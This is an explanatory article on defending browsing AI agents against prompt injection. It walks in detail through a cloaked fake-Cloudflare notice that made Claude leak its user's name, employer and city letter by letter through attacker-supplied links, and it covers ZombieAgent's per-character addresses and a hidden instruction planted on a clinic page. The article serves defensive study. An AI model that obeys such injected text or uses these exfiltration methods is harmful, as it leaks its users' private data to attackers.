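# Layered safeguards for AI agents that browse the web: redirect limits, context isolation and identity checks

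## How a web page can turn a browsing agent against its user

A browsing agent is a language model that opens web pages on a user's behalf and may act on them through software tools. Companies sell such agents as browser extensions, as whole browsers and as features of ordinary chatbots. Claude in Chrome, an extension from the AI developer Anthropic, reads pages, clicks links and fills in forms using the user's existing logins. ChatGPT Atlas, from OpenAI, is a browser with an agent inside it. These agents are both useful and dangerous because they can read what strangers have written while holding the user's information and permissions. A stranger can write a page designed to manipulate the agent into sending them private information, or into dealing with an impostor as if it were the real bank or shop.

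Security engineers combine several safeguards, including rules on which addresses the agent may open, limits on redirects (replies that send the agent's software to another address), separation of private information from browsing, and checks of a page's claimed identity. Each acts at a particular point in the agent's working cycle.

### One turn of the agent

*The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (Kim, Liu and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent as conventional software wrapped around one or more language models, with a memory, tools and an environment to work in. A browsing agent's environment is the web.

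Suppose a woman asks her agent to find a physiotherapist near her office who is free on Tuesday. The software first assembles the context, which is all the text the model receives at a given step. It includes the developer's instructions, descriptions of the tools, her request, and notes the software saved from earlier conversations, which mention her employer, her insurer and a knee operation in the spring. The model can only produce text, so to look up a clinic it writes a tool call, a short structured line that names a tool and its inputs, such as "fetch" and the address of the clinic's page.

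The model has no network connection of its own, so the surrounding software reads its tool call, sends the request, receives the page and adds the page's text to the context as a tool result. The model then runs again over the whole context and produces either another tool call or an answer for the user. Even a simple task can take many rounds.

In this loop, ordinary code sits between the tool call and the actual request, so an engineer can put a rule there that no output of the model can override. The clinic's text normally stays in the context for later rounds, alongside the details about the user's insurer and knee.

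### What a web address gives away

In the address `https://clinic.example/hours/tuesday?insurer=acme`, the scheme, `https`, sets the protocol, and the host, `clinic.example`, identifies the server to contact. A port number may follow the host. If it is missing, the software uses the scheme's default. The scheme, host and port together form the origin, which browsers use to keep one site's data apart from another's. The path, `/hours/tuesday`, follows the host, and the query string, `insurer=acme`, follows the question mark and holds named values.

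Whoever runs the host decides what a URL's path and query mean, and they need not correspond to any document. A server can accept every path and query, return the same ordinary page each time, and record what it receives.

An attacker can steal private data by getting an agent to request a web address that contains it. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that requesting an address also sends that address to the site, and that sites commonly log it. The attacker can then read the data in the log. Encryption doesn't prevent this, because the attacker is the party at the other end of the encrypted connection. The user may not see the request, since it can happen in the background when the software loads an embedded image or previews a link.

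Data can leak through the path of a web address as well as its query string, and through tools other than page fetchers. In September 2025 Simon Willison, a software developer who writes about language model security, described an attack that Abi Raghuram had demonstrated on the agent in Notion, a workplace notes service. Text hidden in a PDF led the agent to put client names and revenue figures in the path of a web address and then submit that address to the web search tool.

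Kim and colleagues class retrieval as a read-only action, a step below sending emails or changing files in their scale of what agents can do. This ranking makes sense for preventing damage to files but works poorly for protecting secrets, because every retrieval from the web also sends information to whoever runs the server.

### Why a page's text can pass for an instruction

Now suppose an attacker built one of the clinic pages in the search results. The attacker adds a passage for AI assistants in type too pale for a human visitor to notice. It says that opening hours depend on the patient's insurer and employer, and that the assistant should include both in the next URL it requests. This doesn't look much like a hijacking, because the user does want the opening hours. The context also contains the patient's insurer and employer, so the model may well produce the tool call.

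A web page can turn a browsing agent against its user through indirect prompt injection, in which an attacker places instructions in content the agent reads to make it serve the attacker. The attack is indirect because the attacker has no access to the AI system and only writes something that the system will later process. This definition follows *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post on the website of the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) by David C, the centre's technical director for platforms research. In his example, a job applicant's CV contains a hidden instruction telling the language model that will score it to approve the application.

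David C's title draws a comparison with SQL injection, an older attack on databases. An attacker types database commands into a web form, and a careless program pastes them into its own query. Programmers can prevent this with parameterised queries, which ensure that the database engine never interprets the user's input as a command. David C argues that language models have no equivalent protection because they have no separate category for commands. A model only predicts the next token (a word or fragment of a word) from the sequence of tokens before it.

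Developers tag each stretch of text as the developer's, the user's or a tool's and train the model to rank these sources, but injections still work. In earlier experiments, moving instructions from one role to another often left the output unchanged. The model may have misidentified whose text it was processing, or it may have identified the source correctly but ignored the ranking. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (2026) reports that misidentification predicts which attacks succeed, both in a diagnostic attack of its own and in standard injections against agents. If that is right, training a model to respect the ranking will fall short while attackers can make it mistake a page's text for the user's.

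Another technique, spotlighting, marks untrusted text more conspicuously. Chrome for Developers (2026), Google's documentation for people who build on its browser, describes a simple version that puts tags around the text. An attacker can defeat it by guessing the closing tag and writing it into the page. A stronger version encodes the untrusted text in Base64, which turns it into strings of letters and digits. This stops the forged tags but uses about a third more tokens. The model still has to decode the text to use it, and at that point it has only another instruction not to obey what it finds. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) calls delimiters and role labels useful engineering practices that create no hard security boundary.

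*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) goes further and claims to prove that perfect prevention is impossible. The argument starts from the fact that current models convert instructions and data into points in the same mathematical space, much as ordinary computers keep programs and data in the same memory. The claim covers only architectures that don't enforce a separation between control and data, and it rules out only perfect prevention. Very low failure rates and enforcement outside the model remain possible.

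Even with better labels, an agent would still have to take some direction from web pages. If it ignored all text written by strangers, it would ignore instructions such as "Choose your branch first" and could not book an appointment.

### The confused deputy and the lethal trifecta

The clinic agent is an example of what security engineers have long called a confused deputy, a program that somebody else misleads into misusing its legitimate authority. The attacker cannot open the woman's stored notes, but her agent can, so the attacker misleads the agent into using its access.

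The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), which the NCSC and agencies from the United States, Canada and New Zealand co-authored, describes a case in which a company lets an agent handle procurement, with broad access to finance systems, email and contracts. An attacker compromises a minor tool in the agent's workflow and uses it to change contracts and approve payments. The audit logs look normal because a trusted identity carried out every action.

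Engineers can fix a confused deputy in a conventional program, but David C thinks language models are "inherently confusable". He advises designers to plan for the worst an attacker could do with direct access to the agent's tools. He also passes on a rule of thumb from a discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. If applied strictly to browsing, this rule would leave an agent with only a stranger's privileges once it opened its first page. Few people would want such a limited agent, but the rule shows how far ordinary designs are from being safe.

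*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) offers a test that is easier to apply. An agent is open to data theft when it combines access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. In the physiotherapist errand, these are the stored notes, the clinic's page and the fetch tool. Removing any one of them prevents the theft, because the attacker needs data to steal, a way to instruct the agent and a way to get the data out.

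Willison advises cutting one of the three, usually external communication, because that tends to reduce usefulness the least. This is awkward for a browsing agent because it cannot read a live page without requesting the page's address, so the same request exposes it to outside content and communicates externally. Designers therefore tend to restrict which addresses the agent may request. An attack on Claude that Willison reported in July 2026 showed that such restrictions can have gaps.

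The trifecta is a test for data theft, but injection can do other harm. OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an attack found by the company's own automated attacker, which planted an email in a user's inbox. When the user later asked for an out-of-office reply, the agent came across the email and sent the chief executive a resignation letter in the user's name. The attack required only untrusted text and the power to act, and no secret had to reach the attacker. An agent that cannot leak anything may therefore still need checks on whom it is dealing with and what it is about to do.

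### Whether anyone can eliminate injection

David C writes that prompt injection may never be "totally mitigated" in the way SQL injection can be, and warns readers to beware of products that claim to stop it. His post is a signed argument and carries less formal weight than official guidance. The joint guidance of May 2026, which the NCSC co-authored, recommends that organisations use agentic AI only for low-risk and non-sensitive tasks. Infosecurity Magazine's *NCSC Urges Stronger Controls for Agentic AI Systems* reports that in August 2026 the NCSC issued interim advice not to rely solely on safeguards built into a model, and to deny agents network connections by default where possible.

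The developers say much the same about their own products. OpenAI considers injection "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'" and likens it to scams aimed at people. Chrome for Developers states that safety cannot be guaranteed inside the model because language models are probabilistic. Anthropic wrote in November 2025 that "no browser agent is immune to prompt injection". These admissions go against the companies' commercial interests, which is a reason to believe them.

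Anthropic has since become more confident. Its *Claude in Chrome is generally available* reports attack success rates at or near zero for newer models in the company's own tests with all safeguards on. But it still calls injection a moving target, and Anthropic's help page tells users that browsing "still carries inherent risks". When Anthropic published similar results for its coding agent in August 2026, its employee Thariq Shihipar said the post's title should have included "defeating the lethal trifecta". Willison replied that he would love to believe it but wanted more independent confirmation. His caution seems right, since tests against today's attacks can't show whether the safeguards will stop new ones.

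### Defence in depth

If the model will sometimes follow the wrong instructions, the system around it has to limit the consequences. Defence in depth means using several safeguards so that when one fails, another can still stop the attacker. The joint guidance lists it among the proven principles of cyber security, and OpenAI describes its check on web addresses as one layer in such a strategy.

How much a second safeguard helps depends on whether it misses the same attacks as the first. Two safeguards that each miss one attack in ten will together miss only one in a hundred if their misses are unrelated, but still one in ten if the same wording fools both. A detector and the agent it guards could easily be fooled by the same wording if they are built on similar language models.

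For this reason, the kind of safeguard matters more than the number of safeguards. A deterministic safeguard is a rule that ordinary code enforces whatever the model decides, such as an allowlist, which restricts the software to listed domains or addresses. Probabilistic safeguards rely on a model's judgement. They include training against known attacks, classifiers that scan pages, and a second model that reviews each action. Published guidance sometimes mixes the two kinds. Chrome for Developers lists a system instruction about untrusted content among its deterministic guardrails but explains it under the probabilistic ones. The instruction is probabilistic because the model may fail to follow it.

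Willison objects to relying on judgement because "99% is a failing grade" in security, where an attacker can keep trying until an attack succeeds. Code has a different weakness because it applies its rule every time, even where the rule's author overlooked something. David C wants designers to put more effort into deterministic safeguards, while OpenAI says that the nature of injection makes deterministic guarantees challenging. Both can be right, because a rule in code can guarantee that a misled model contacts only servers on the list, even though it cannot guarantee that a page will not mislead the model.

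Against an attack like the one on the clinic's visitor, each safeguard comes in at a different step.

| Safeguard | Step it interrupts | What it rests on |
|---|---|---|
| Detectors that scan pages | The hidden passage reaches the model unnoticed | A model's judgement |
| Identity checks | The agent takes the attacker's page for the clinic it names | Code where an exact match decides, otherwise judgement |
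| Checks against independent sources | The agent accepts a false claim on the page | Mostly judgement |
| Context isolation (private information stays out of the session that reads pages or writes requests) | The passage and the user's notes meet in one context | Code |
| Information-flow control (labels on data that block forbidden transfers) | The agent carries data from one site to another | Code |
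| Allowlists and URL provenance rules (the agent may open only addresses from approved sources) | The agent requests an address with private data in it | Code |
| Redirect limits | A permitted address forwards the request to the attacker's server | Code |
| User approval | The agent sends, books or pays | The user's attention |

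## The fake coffee shop attack on Claude, step by step

In July 2026 the developer Ayush Paul showed that a website could obtain a user's name, employer and home city from Claude, Anthropic's assistant, while the user thought Claude was reading about a coffee shop. He attacked the chatbot at claude.ai, with no experimental settings or add-ons, and took only his own data. *The Memory Heist* (Paul, 2026) recounts the steps in the order he found them, including the dead ends, and shows which safeguards held and where the data got out.

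### What Claude knew and what it could open

Claude.ai had two kinds of memory. The software condensed the user's recent conversations once a day into a few paragraphs, which it added to the context of every conversation. Claude could also call a tool that searched the full history. Paul argues that AI memory systems hold more information than most password managers, because people tell assistants about confidential work, secrets and relationships.

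He chose Claude's fetch tool to get this information out. It sends only GET requests, the kind a browser uses to load a page, so an attacker could put data only in the address. Paul set up a server that recorded every request and asked Claude to open an address on it with his name in the path. The tool blocked the request.

After some experimenting he worked out the rule. The tool would open an address only if one of these things was true:

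- the user had put the address in a message
- Claude's search tool had returned it
- a page that the tool had already fetched linked to it

This is a URL provenance rule, and it stops the simplest kind of theft. Willison explained in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (2026) that if an attacker tells the model to add the user's recent answers to the end of an address and open it, the tool will refuse because that exact address has never come from an approved source.

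### An alphabet of links

Claude was allowed to open links on pages it had fetched, so it could move around a website as a person does. But a website's owner decides which links it contains. Paul put 26 links on his home page, one for each letter of the alphabet, and asked Claude to open the link for the first letter of his name. His log showed a request for `/a`.

He then made the server generate further pages on demand. Each page linked to addresses one character longer, using the 26 letters and a hyphen, so `/a` linked to `/aa`, `/ab` and so on. When Paul asked Claude to spell his name by following these links, the log recorded requests for `/a`, then `/ay`, then `/ayu`, reaching `/ayush-paul` on the tenth request. There are about 200 trillion possible ten-character paths, but the server only had to generate the pages Claude requested.

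All of these requests complied with the rule because Claude didn't compose any of the addresses; Paul's server had supplied them as links. The code checked where each address came from, but Claude's choice of which address to request revealed private information. Each choice revealed one character, and Claude could reveal more by following more links.

### A notice in Cloudflare's name

So far Claude had spelled the name because its own user had asked it to. A real attacker would need the page to make Claude do the same. Paul's first few injections worked unreliably, and a story about a loyalty scheme was too contrived to fool Claude.

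Paul had more success with a story about Cloudflare, a company that protects many websites from unwanted automated traffic. He based the story on the fact that Cloudflare really does turn AI agents away from websites. Claude's first visit to his server had failed because Cloudflare had, without his consent, given the site a restrictive `robots.txt`, a file that tells automated visitors which pages they may open.

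Paul disguised the site as a coffee shop's and put a fake Cloudflare security check in front of it. In the notice, he claimed that Cloudflare now let AI assistants in if they gave the name of the person they were working for, and that Claude would have to do this letter by letter because of the limitations of its fetch tool. The claim about the tool was partly true, since it would have refused an address that Claude had composed from the name, so Paul was using Anthropic's safeguard to justify the strange procedure that got around it.

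The notice presented the user's name as a requirement for reading about the coffee shop, which the user had asked Claude to do. It contained no instruction to abandon that task, so a detector that looks for commands to ignore earlier instructions would have found none.

People who visited the site did not see the notice. A program that requests a web page normally sends a label, called the user agent, that identifies the software, and Claude's includes "Claude-User". Paul's server sent the notice only to visitors with that label, a technique called cloaking. A suspicious user who opened the same address in a browser would have seen an ordinary coffee shop website.

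### What leaked

Paul's server recovered his full name, his employer, Beem, and his home city of Charlotte, North Carolina. Hackaday's *This Week In Security* (2026) explains that once Claude had accepted the false login procedure, the site could request other details Claude had about its user, beyond the name. In *The Read-Only Lie*, a blog post that Claude helped draft, dyb puts the total at roughly 30 characters, and therefore about 30 fetches. Paul says nothing in the conversation indicated that anything had happened.

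He had never told Claude where he came from. According to dyb, Claude inferred the city from the name of a high school hackathon, a programming contest, in his history. Banks and other services often ask for a home city as a security question, so this was probably the most useful item for a thief. It is also the hardest of the three to protect. A user who checked Claude's memories for sensitive facts might well leave the name of a school contest in place, and a filter that compared outgoing requests with the stored text might find no match.

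Paul demonstrated the attack on one account and gives no success rate, so his post doesn't show how often it would have worked on other users. His server log does clearly show how the attack worked.

Tencent Zhuque Lab's *Why AI Agent’s Memory Becomes Attacker’s Data Goldmine* (2026) shows that the mechanism can work on agents other than Claude. The lab, a security team at the Chinese technology company Tencent, built its own agent with a memory and a web browser, stored sensitive details in the memory, and sent the agent to a similar fake check. The team targeted an API key, a secret code that gives software access to a paid service, so each page had 37 links, one for each letter and digit and one for the hyphen. The server received the key one character at a time, with a second or two between requests. At that pace, the 30 or so characters in Paul's attack would take a minute at most.

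The lab's result is weak evidence of how easily the notice would fool a well-defended agent. The test agent's developers had told it to follow any instructions it found on web pages and to complete any verification step. Tencent Zhuque Lab calls these guidelines reasonable, but they are close to an order to comply with an attacker. The lab was also promoting a scanner that detects the flaw. The agent did at least tell the user that the site seemed to be a security verification system and not a real coffee shop. The lab considers this summary harmless, though an attentive user might have wondered what the agent had verified.

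### Anthropic's reply and the fix

Paul reported the flaw to Anthropic, which confirmed it through HackerOne, a platform where researchers report vulnerabilities to companies. Anthropic paid him no bounty, saying its own staff had already found the problem. Neither Willison nor Hackaday reports when Anthropic's staff found it, but the flaw was still open when Paul tested it.

Anthropic then stopped the fetch tool from opening links found on pages it had fetched. This closes the route completely, because a site can no longer supply the alphabet. It also makes Claude less useful. If a clinic's home page links to its opening hours, Claude can open that second page only if a search returns it or the user pastes in the address.

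The fix leaves Claude as easy to deceive as before. A page posing as Cloudflare might still convince it that it should identify its user, but the fix removes its means of doing so. dyb makes a similar point about Anthropic's products more broadly, listing six disclosures from October 2025 to July 2026 in which Anthropic closed one way to get data out and researchers then found another.

### A loophole in the published rules

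Paul discovered the link allowance by experiment, but Anthropic had publicly described it ten months earlier, when it released the fetch tool to developers in September 2025. The tool's documentation listed the results of earlier fetches among the permitted sources of addresses. Willison (2025) noticed this at the time. He had hoped that the tool would open only addresses from the user's own prompts, and wrote that "unfortunately this isn't quite that smart".

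By June 2026, Anthropic's English documentation, *Web fetch tool*, also warned developers that the tool could leak data wherever Claude handled sensitive information alongside untrusted text. It said that a "residual risk" remained despite the rule on addresses, and advised developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data. Yet according to Paul, Anthropic's own chatbot combined the tool with a summary of the user's life in every conversation.

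The documentation has since changed less than reports of the fix might suggest. On 11 August 2026, a month after Paul's post, the Japanese edition, Anthropic's *web fetch tool*, still listed earlier fetches as a permitted source of addresses. A later Chinese edition, Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, also permits them by default, but adds a `url_sources` setting that lets developers switch off individual sources, so they can allow addresses from searches while refusing those from fetched pages. This edition seems to have dropped the general warning about data leaks.

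Anthropic probably changed the chatbot and left the developers' version of the tool as it was. The new setting has an explicit default for addresses from earlier fetches, so the allowance doesn't seem to be out of date. If the documentation is accurate, a company that builds its own agent on the fetch tool and gives it access to customer records still has to close Paul's loophole itself.

The same edition describes a new check that makes the tool refuse any address that appears to contain a password or an API key, unless the developer's instructions or the user's message include that credential. This wouldn't have protected Paul, because names and cities aren't credentials. It might also come too late for a key that leaks character by character, because the server would have most of the key by the time an address contained enough of it to be recognized.

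### What would have stopped it

Even a limit of zero redirects would have let every letter through, because Paul's server didn't use redirects. It answered each request with an ordinary page, and Claude chose each link itself and opened it with a new call to the fetch tool.

A cap on the number of fetches would have reduced the damage. Anthropic lets developers set such a cap, which has no default value, and its sample code sets it to five. With that cap, Claude could have opened the home page and four letter pages, and the log would have ended at `/ayus`. The attacker could have tried to get the remaining letters if the user's next message sent Claude back to the site.

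dyb proposes letting Claude follow links only on domains that the user has named in the conversation. That would protect a user whose search happened to turn up the coffee shop, but not one who had given Claude the shop's address. Another of dyb's suggestions is a detector for repeated requests to one site in which each path is a single character longer than the last. An attacker could evade this by giving the links arbitrary names and keeping a list of the letter each one stood for.

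The table lists the conditions the attack relied on. All were essential except cloaking and the lack of a cap on fetches. Without cloaking, the theft would have been easier to notice, and a cap would have made it yield less.

| What the attack relied on | Safeguard that would have removed it | Cost or remaining gap |
|---|---|---|
| The user's memories and the attacker's page were in the same context | Context isolation: Claude opens pages in a session without the memories | Claude can't use what it knows about the user while it browses |
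| Claude treated the notice as Cloudflare's | An identity check on the domain that served the notice | An attacker can try a story that names no other company |
| Claude believed that Cloudflare asks assistants for their users' names | A check against Cloudflare's own published information | Claude must judge when a claim needs checking |
| The fetch tool opened links from pages it had fetched | A URL provenance rule without that source, which was Anthropic's fix | Claude can't click through a website |
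| Claude could contact a server that the attacker ran | An allowlist of approved domains | Claude can't visit a shop that nobody has approved |
| Private information could determine which link Claude opened | Information-flow control that covers choices as well as copied text | Claude can't choose links on the basis of private facts |
| Claude could open dozens of pages in a row | A cap on fetches | The first few characters still leak |
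| Claude opened each link without asking the user | User approval for every link | Users may approve dozens of harmless-looking requests without reading them |
| People saw a normal coffee shop at the same address | A second fetch under an ordinary browser's label, to compare the two versions | The attacker can show everyone the notice and accept a higher risk of discovery |

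## Rules on which addresses an agent may open

Anthropic ended Paul's attack on Claude by changing which addresses the fetch tool would open. Ideally, such a rule would block exactly the addresses that reveal something private. But code can't recognise private information in every form, so developers make it check something simpler: which host the address points to, where in the conversation the address came from, or whether the address was public before the conversation began. An attacker then looks for requests that pass the check and still reveal something private.

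### Listing the permitted domains

Developers who use Anthropic's fetch tool can enter an allowlist of domains in the `allowed_domains` setting. An entry for `example.com` also covers subdomains such as `docs.example.com`, and an entry such as `example.com/blog` limits the agent to one part of a site. When Claude requests an address outside the list, it gets an error instead of the page and continues with its task.

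The Cyrillic letter "а" looks the same as the Latin "a", so a developer could mistakenly approve `аmazon.com` with the Cyrillic letter, which is a different domain from `amazon.com`. Anthropic advises developers to use ASCII names in their lists of approved domains where they can and to check the lists for suspicious characters.

With an allowlist, a misled model can still write private facts into an address, but only the listed hosts will receive them. Willison (2025) considers this much stronger than the fetch tool's default rule, provided that nobody can use the listed domains to get data out. He calls finding domains that meet this condition "a tricky proposition", because many respectable hosts store or forward whatever strangers send them. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes an attack that saved a user's last conversation to a file and sent it out through Anthropic's file storage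 service, which Claude's software was allowed to contact.

Shared hosting causes the same problem. A developer who approves `s3.amazonaws.com`, the address of Amazon's storage service, approves every customer's files there, including an attacker's. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* therefore recommends approving a particular host, path and owner together. Redirects can also send a request from an approved host to another.

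Allowlists greatly restrict general browsing because nobody can list in advance every site a user might ask about, such as a clinic's. OpenAI also argues that strict lists produce so many warnings that people learn to click through them. Allowlists suit agents with a narrow job, such as answering questions from a company's own manuals.

### Refusing addresses the model wrote

Anthropic's URL provenance rule applies whether or not the developer sets an allowlist. In the developers' version of the fetch tool, the rule allows addresses from the three sources Paul identified and from the results of tools that the developer's software runs. According to Anthropic, it doesn't allow an address that appears only in Claude's own output or only in the developer's standing instructions. If Claude tries to open one, it receives an error and has to look for another way to do the task.

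The rule is meant to prevent Claude from ever opening an address it composed itself. Claude can open only complete addresses that someone else supplied, so it can't try `/hours` to find a clinic's opening hours or search the clinic's site by editing the query string.

The code checks only where an address appeared, though, not who wrote it. Willison pointed out that many applications paste untrusted material into the user's message. If an email assistant does this with each incoming email, the tool will treat a stranger's links as the user's own.

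A tool that repeats Claude's text back to it creates a worse gap. If a developer gives Claude a tool for running programs, Claude can write a program that prints an address naming the user's insurer. That address is now part of a tool result, and the fetch tool accepts addresses from tool results by default. Anthropic's documentation describes this problem and notes that an error message quoting Claude's text can have the same effect. Combining such a tool with the default settings leaves very little protection, because a malicious page only has to get Claude to take one extra step.

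Developers can close this gap with the `url_sources` setting, by listing either the tools whose results don't count as sources or the only tools whose results do. The second option is safer because it excludes any tool the developer adds later. Anthropic's hosted tool for running code never counts as a source, so the gap concerns tools that developers run themselves.

### Opening only addresses that are already public

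OpenAI tried several weaker rules before its present one. In early 2023 Johann Rehberger, a security researcher, reported that a malicious page could get ChatGPT to display an image whose address contained data from the conversation. In December 2023 OpenAI added a check in which the chat page queried OpenAI's servers about whether each image was "safe" to load. Willison, in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, thought this a strange fix because OpenAI had not blocked images from outside domains. Rehberger later bypassed the check and, in Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection*, showed that someone who wrote a web page or PDF could obtain a user's past chats.

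OpenAI then forbade ChatGPT to change an address before opening it, even by adding something to the end. In September 2025 the security company Radware got around this rule with an attack it named ZombieAgent. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes an email with 37 ready-made addresses, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail account, ChatGPT read the email, found the information the attacker wanted and opened the address for each character in turn. The rule didn't stop the attack because ChatGPT never changed an address.

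Radware's researchers also made a version that kept the characters in order by giving each character a separate address for each position, so `a0` meant an "a" in the first place and `a1` an "a" in the second. A ten-character block of letters and digits takes 360 addresses. Radware claims a 100% success rate for an improved version of the attack but doesn't state how many attempts it made.

Radware reported the flaw on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. Radware does not describe the fix. According to the press report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, OpenAI restricted which links ChatGPT could open from emails, and links in a well-known public index were among those allowed.

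Under a general rule OpenAI set out in January 2026, software checks whether the company's crawler has already recorded an exact address before an agent automatically loads a page or image from it. The crawler is a program that explores the web and records the addresses it finds, and it has no access to users' conversations or accounts. If the agent has just put the name of a user's insurer into an address, the crawler is very unlikely to have recorded it.

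If there is no match, the software either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation. The user can then copy the link or open it anyway, so the safeguard depends on the user's attention. Legitimate pages will also fail the check if they are too new or obscure for the crawler to have found, as will most links that a site generates for one visitor.

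OpenAI describes the guarantee narrowly, as preventing the agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself", but even that slightly overstates the protection. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger reports that OpenAI's technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, acknowledges a remaining leak through separate addresses for each letter. An attacker with an ordinary blog may already have 36 pages in the index, and can tell the model which page stands for which character. Someone with thousands of pages could assign them to whole words.

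The crawler rule blocks Paul's method of generating pages on demand, since the crawler can't have recorded pages that don't exist yet, so the attacker has to publish the whole alphabet in advance and wait for the crawler to find it.

The table shows how the three rules would treat the same requests. It assumes that the allowlist contains a large search engine but neither the clinic's site nor the attacker's, and that Anthropic's rule is on its default settings.

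| Request | Domain allowlist | Anthropic's provenance rule | OpenAI's crawler rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| A clinic's home page, from a search result | Refuses | Opens | Opens if the crawler has recorded it |
| The clinic's page for next Tuesday, linked from its home page | Refuses | Opens | Probably warns the user or sends the agent elsewhere |
| An attacker's address to which the model has added the user's insurer | Refuses | Refuses | Warns the user or sends the agent elsewhere |
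| An attacker's page for the letter "a", published months ago and linked from a page the agent has read | Refuses | Opens | Opens if the crawler has recorded it |
| An address on the search engine to which the model has added private data | Opens | Refuses | Warns the user or sends the agent elsewhere |

### How much a choice of links can reveal

Suppose an agent makes N fetches and picks each time from k permitted links. It could produce k × k × … × k different sequences, or kᴺ in all, and the attacker's log shows which one it produced. Information theory measures this in bits, where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. The log can reveal up to

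**N × log₂(k) bits.**

With 26 links, each choice reveals about 4.7 bits, so ten choices reveal about 47 bits, enough to identify one possibility among 141 trillion. The true limit is slightly higher, because the agent can also convey information by stopping early or varying the time between requests. A real name reveals less than the maximum, because the attacker could have guessed some of the letters.

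An agent can leak far more data through an address it writes freely than by choosing among existing links. Anthropic's fetch tool rejects addresses longer than 250 characters. If the scheme and host use 30 of these, the remaining 220 can hold private data. Each character carries 6 bits if there are 64 to choose from, so a single request could reveal 1,320 bits. An agent choosing among 26 links would need 281 choices to reveal as much.

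*Takedown* (2025), a study of attacks on coding agents, found this worst case in one agent. Its fetch tool required no user approval, so an attacker could make the agent send out anything in its context, including the contents of open files. Combined with another flaw that let the attacker read files at will, the tool could leak any file on the user's machine.

Against an agent like that, restricting the model to existing links makes theft hundreds of times slower. This slowdown matters a lot for documents but hardly at all for short secrets. The table gives the smallest number of choices that can identify each item.

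| Private item | Bits | Choices among 26 links | Choices among 1,000 links |
|---|---|---|---|
| A date of birth within the past century | 15.2 | 4 | 2 |
| A six-digit security code | 19.9 | 5 | 2 |
| A ten-digit phone number | 33.2 | 8 | 4 |
| A random 128-bit key | 128 | 28 | 13 |

Even a thousand links can be easy for the model to use. If the links stand for 000 to 999, it can send a six-digit code by opening one link for the first three digits and another for the last three. The figures for the 26 links assume a more efficient encoding than most injected instructions would use, so a real attack would often need more fetches.

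### What a cap on fetches buys

Anthropic's `max_uses` setting limits how many times an agent can fetch a page. A limit of five would have held Paul's attack to four letters. Four choices among 26 links reveal at most 18.8 bits, slightly less than a six-digit code requires. If each choice were among 1,000 links, four choices could reveal almost 40 bits, enough for a phone number.

The cap is therefore weaker than it seems, because the developer controls the number of choices (N) but the attacker controls the number of links per page (k). If the developer halves N, the attacker can compensate by squaring k, say from 26 to 676. Anthropic estimates that a typical 10-kilobyte page is about 2,500 tokens, and at 40 bytes per link such a page could hold 250 links. Limiting how much of each page the model sees would help very little, because halving the number of links removes only one bit from each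 choice.

*Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) reports that ChatGPT at the time opened at most ten addresses per prompt, which limited the paper's attack to ten characters per prompt. Opening several addresses also took longer than opening one, so users had more chance to notice the attack and stop it.

Anthropic's cap applies to one turn, roughly the work Claude does in answer to one message. Failed fetches count towards it. The count restarts with each turn, so a cap of five would allow a hundred fetches over twenty messages. An attacker who can reach the agent repeatedly can therefore collect a secret in instalments. Radware showed one way to do this by getting ChatGPT to store malicious instructions in its memory, which it then carried out before answering each new message.

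In Managed Agents, a service in which Anthropic supplies a ready-made set of tools, the fetch tool is on by default and developers can't set `max_uses`. A research agent that reads dozens of sources would need a high cap anyway. A separate limit for each unfamiliar site, counted over the whole conversation, would interfere less with such an agent and better restrict an attacker who has only one domain.

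### Caching pages and forbidding repeat visits

Rehberger proposes two further measures on Embrace The Red. The software could cache each page, keeping a copy for a few minutes and using it if the agent requested the page again. Or it could forbid the agent to visit the same full address twice in a session. Either way, an attacker with one fixed page per letter would receive each letter only once, so the name "Anna" would arrive as "an".

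Some agents already do this for other reasons. According to Mintlify, a documentation site, the fetch tool in Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, has a 15-minute cache, so a repeat request within that time never reaches the website. The research agent in *PatchScout* (2026) never revisits an address within a run, mainly to avoid burdening the sites it reads.

In theory, banning an agent from opening the same page twice only slightly reduces how much an attacker can learn. An agent that opens ten of 26 pages in a chosen order can still reveal about 44 bits, compared with 47 if it may repeat pages. The ban matters more over a long session, because the attacker eventually runs out of pages. If the agent can open each of the 26 pages only once, it can reveal at most about 90 bits in total, however many fetches it is allowed.

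To use even those bits, the attacker needs a code that never repeats a page. ZombieAgent's numbered addresses are one such code, because an "a" in the first position has a different address from an "a" in the second. Nested links are another. When Claude followed Paul's links, it opened `/a`, `/ay` and `/ayu`. Each page was new, so neither a cache nor a ban would have stopped any of the letters.

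The value of Rehberger's proposals thus depends on which rule they accompany. OpenAI's crawler rule limits the attacker to pages that already exist, so the attacker runs out of them if the agent can't open the same page twice. Under a provenance rule that accepts links from fetched pages, the attacker can keep generating new addresses, and a ban on repeat visits achieves almost nothing. Caching disrupts ordinary use less than a ban does, because an agent that returns to a list of clinics still gets the saved list, though it may miss an appointment that opened a minute ago.

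Zenity Labs' *Sure, Let AI Browse the Internet* recommends letting the agent ask a trusted third party to look at a website and report what the agent needs to know. If the third party answers from copies it cached before the conversation, the site's owner receives no request and learns nothing from the agent's choice of pages. However, the third party learns what the agent asked for, and stored copies can't show whether a physiotherapist is free on Tuesday or let anyone make a booking.

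### Requests that other software makes

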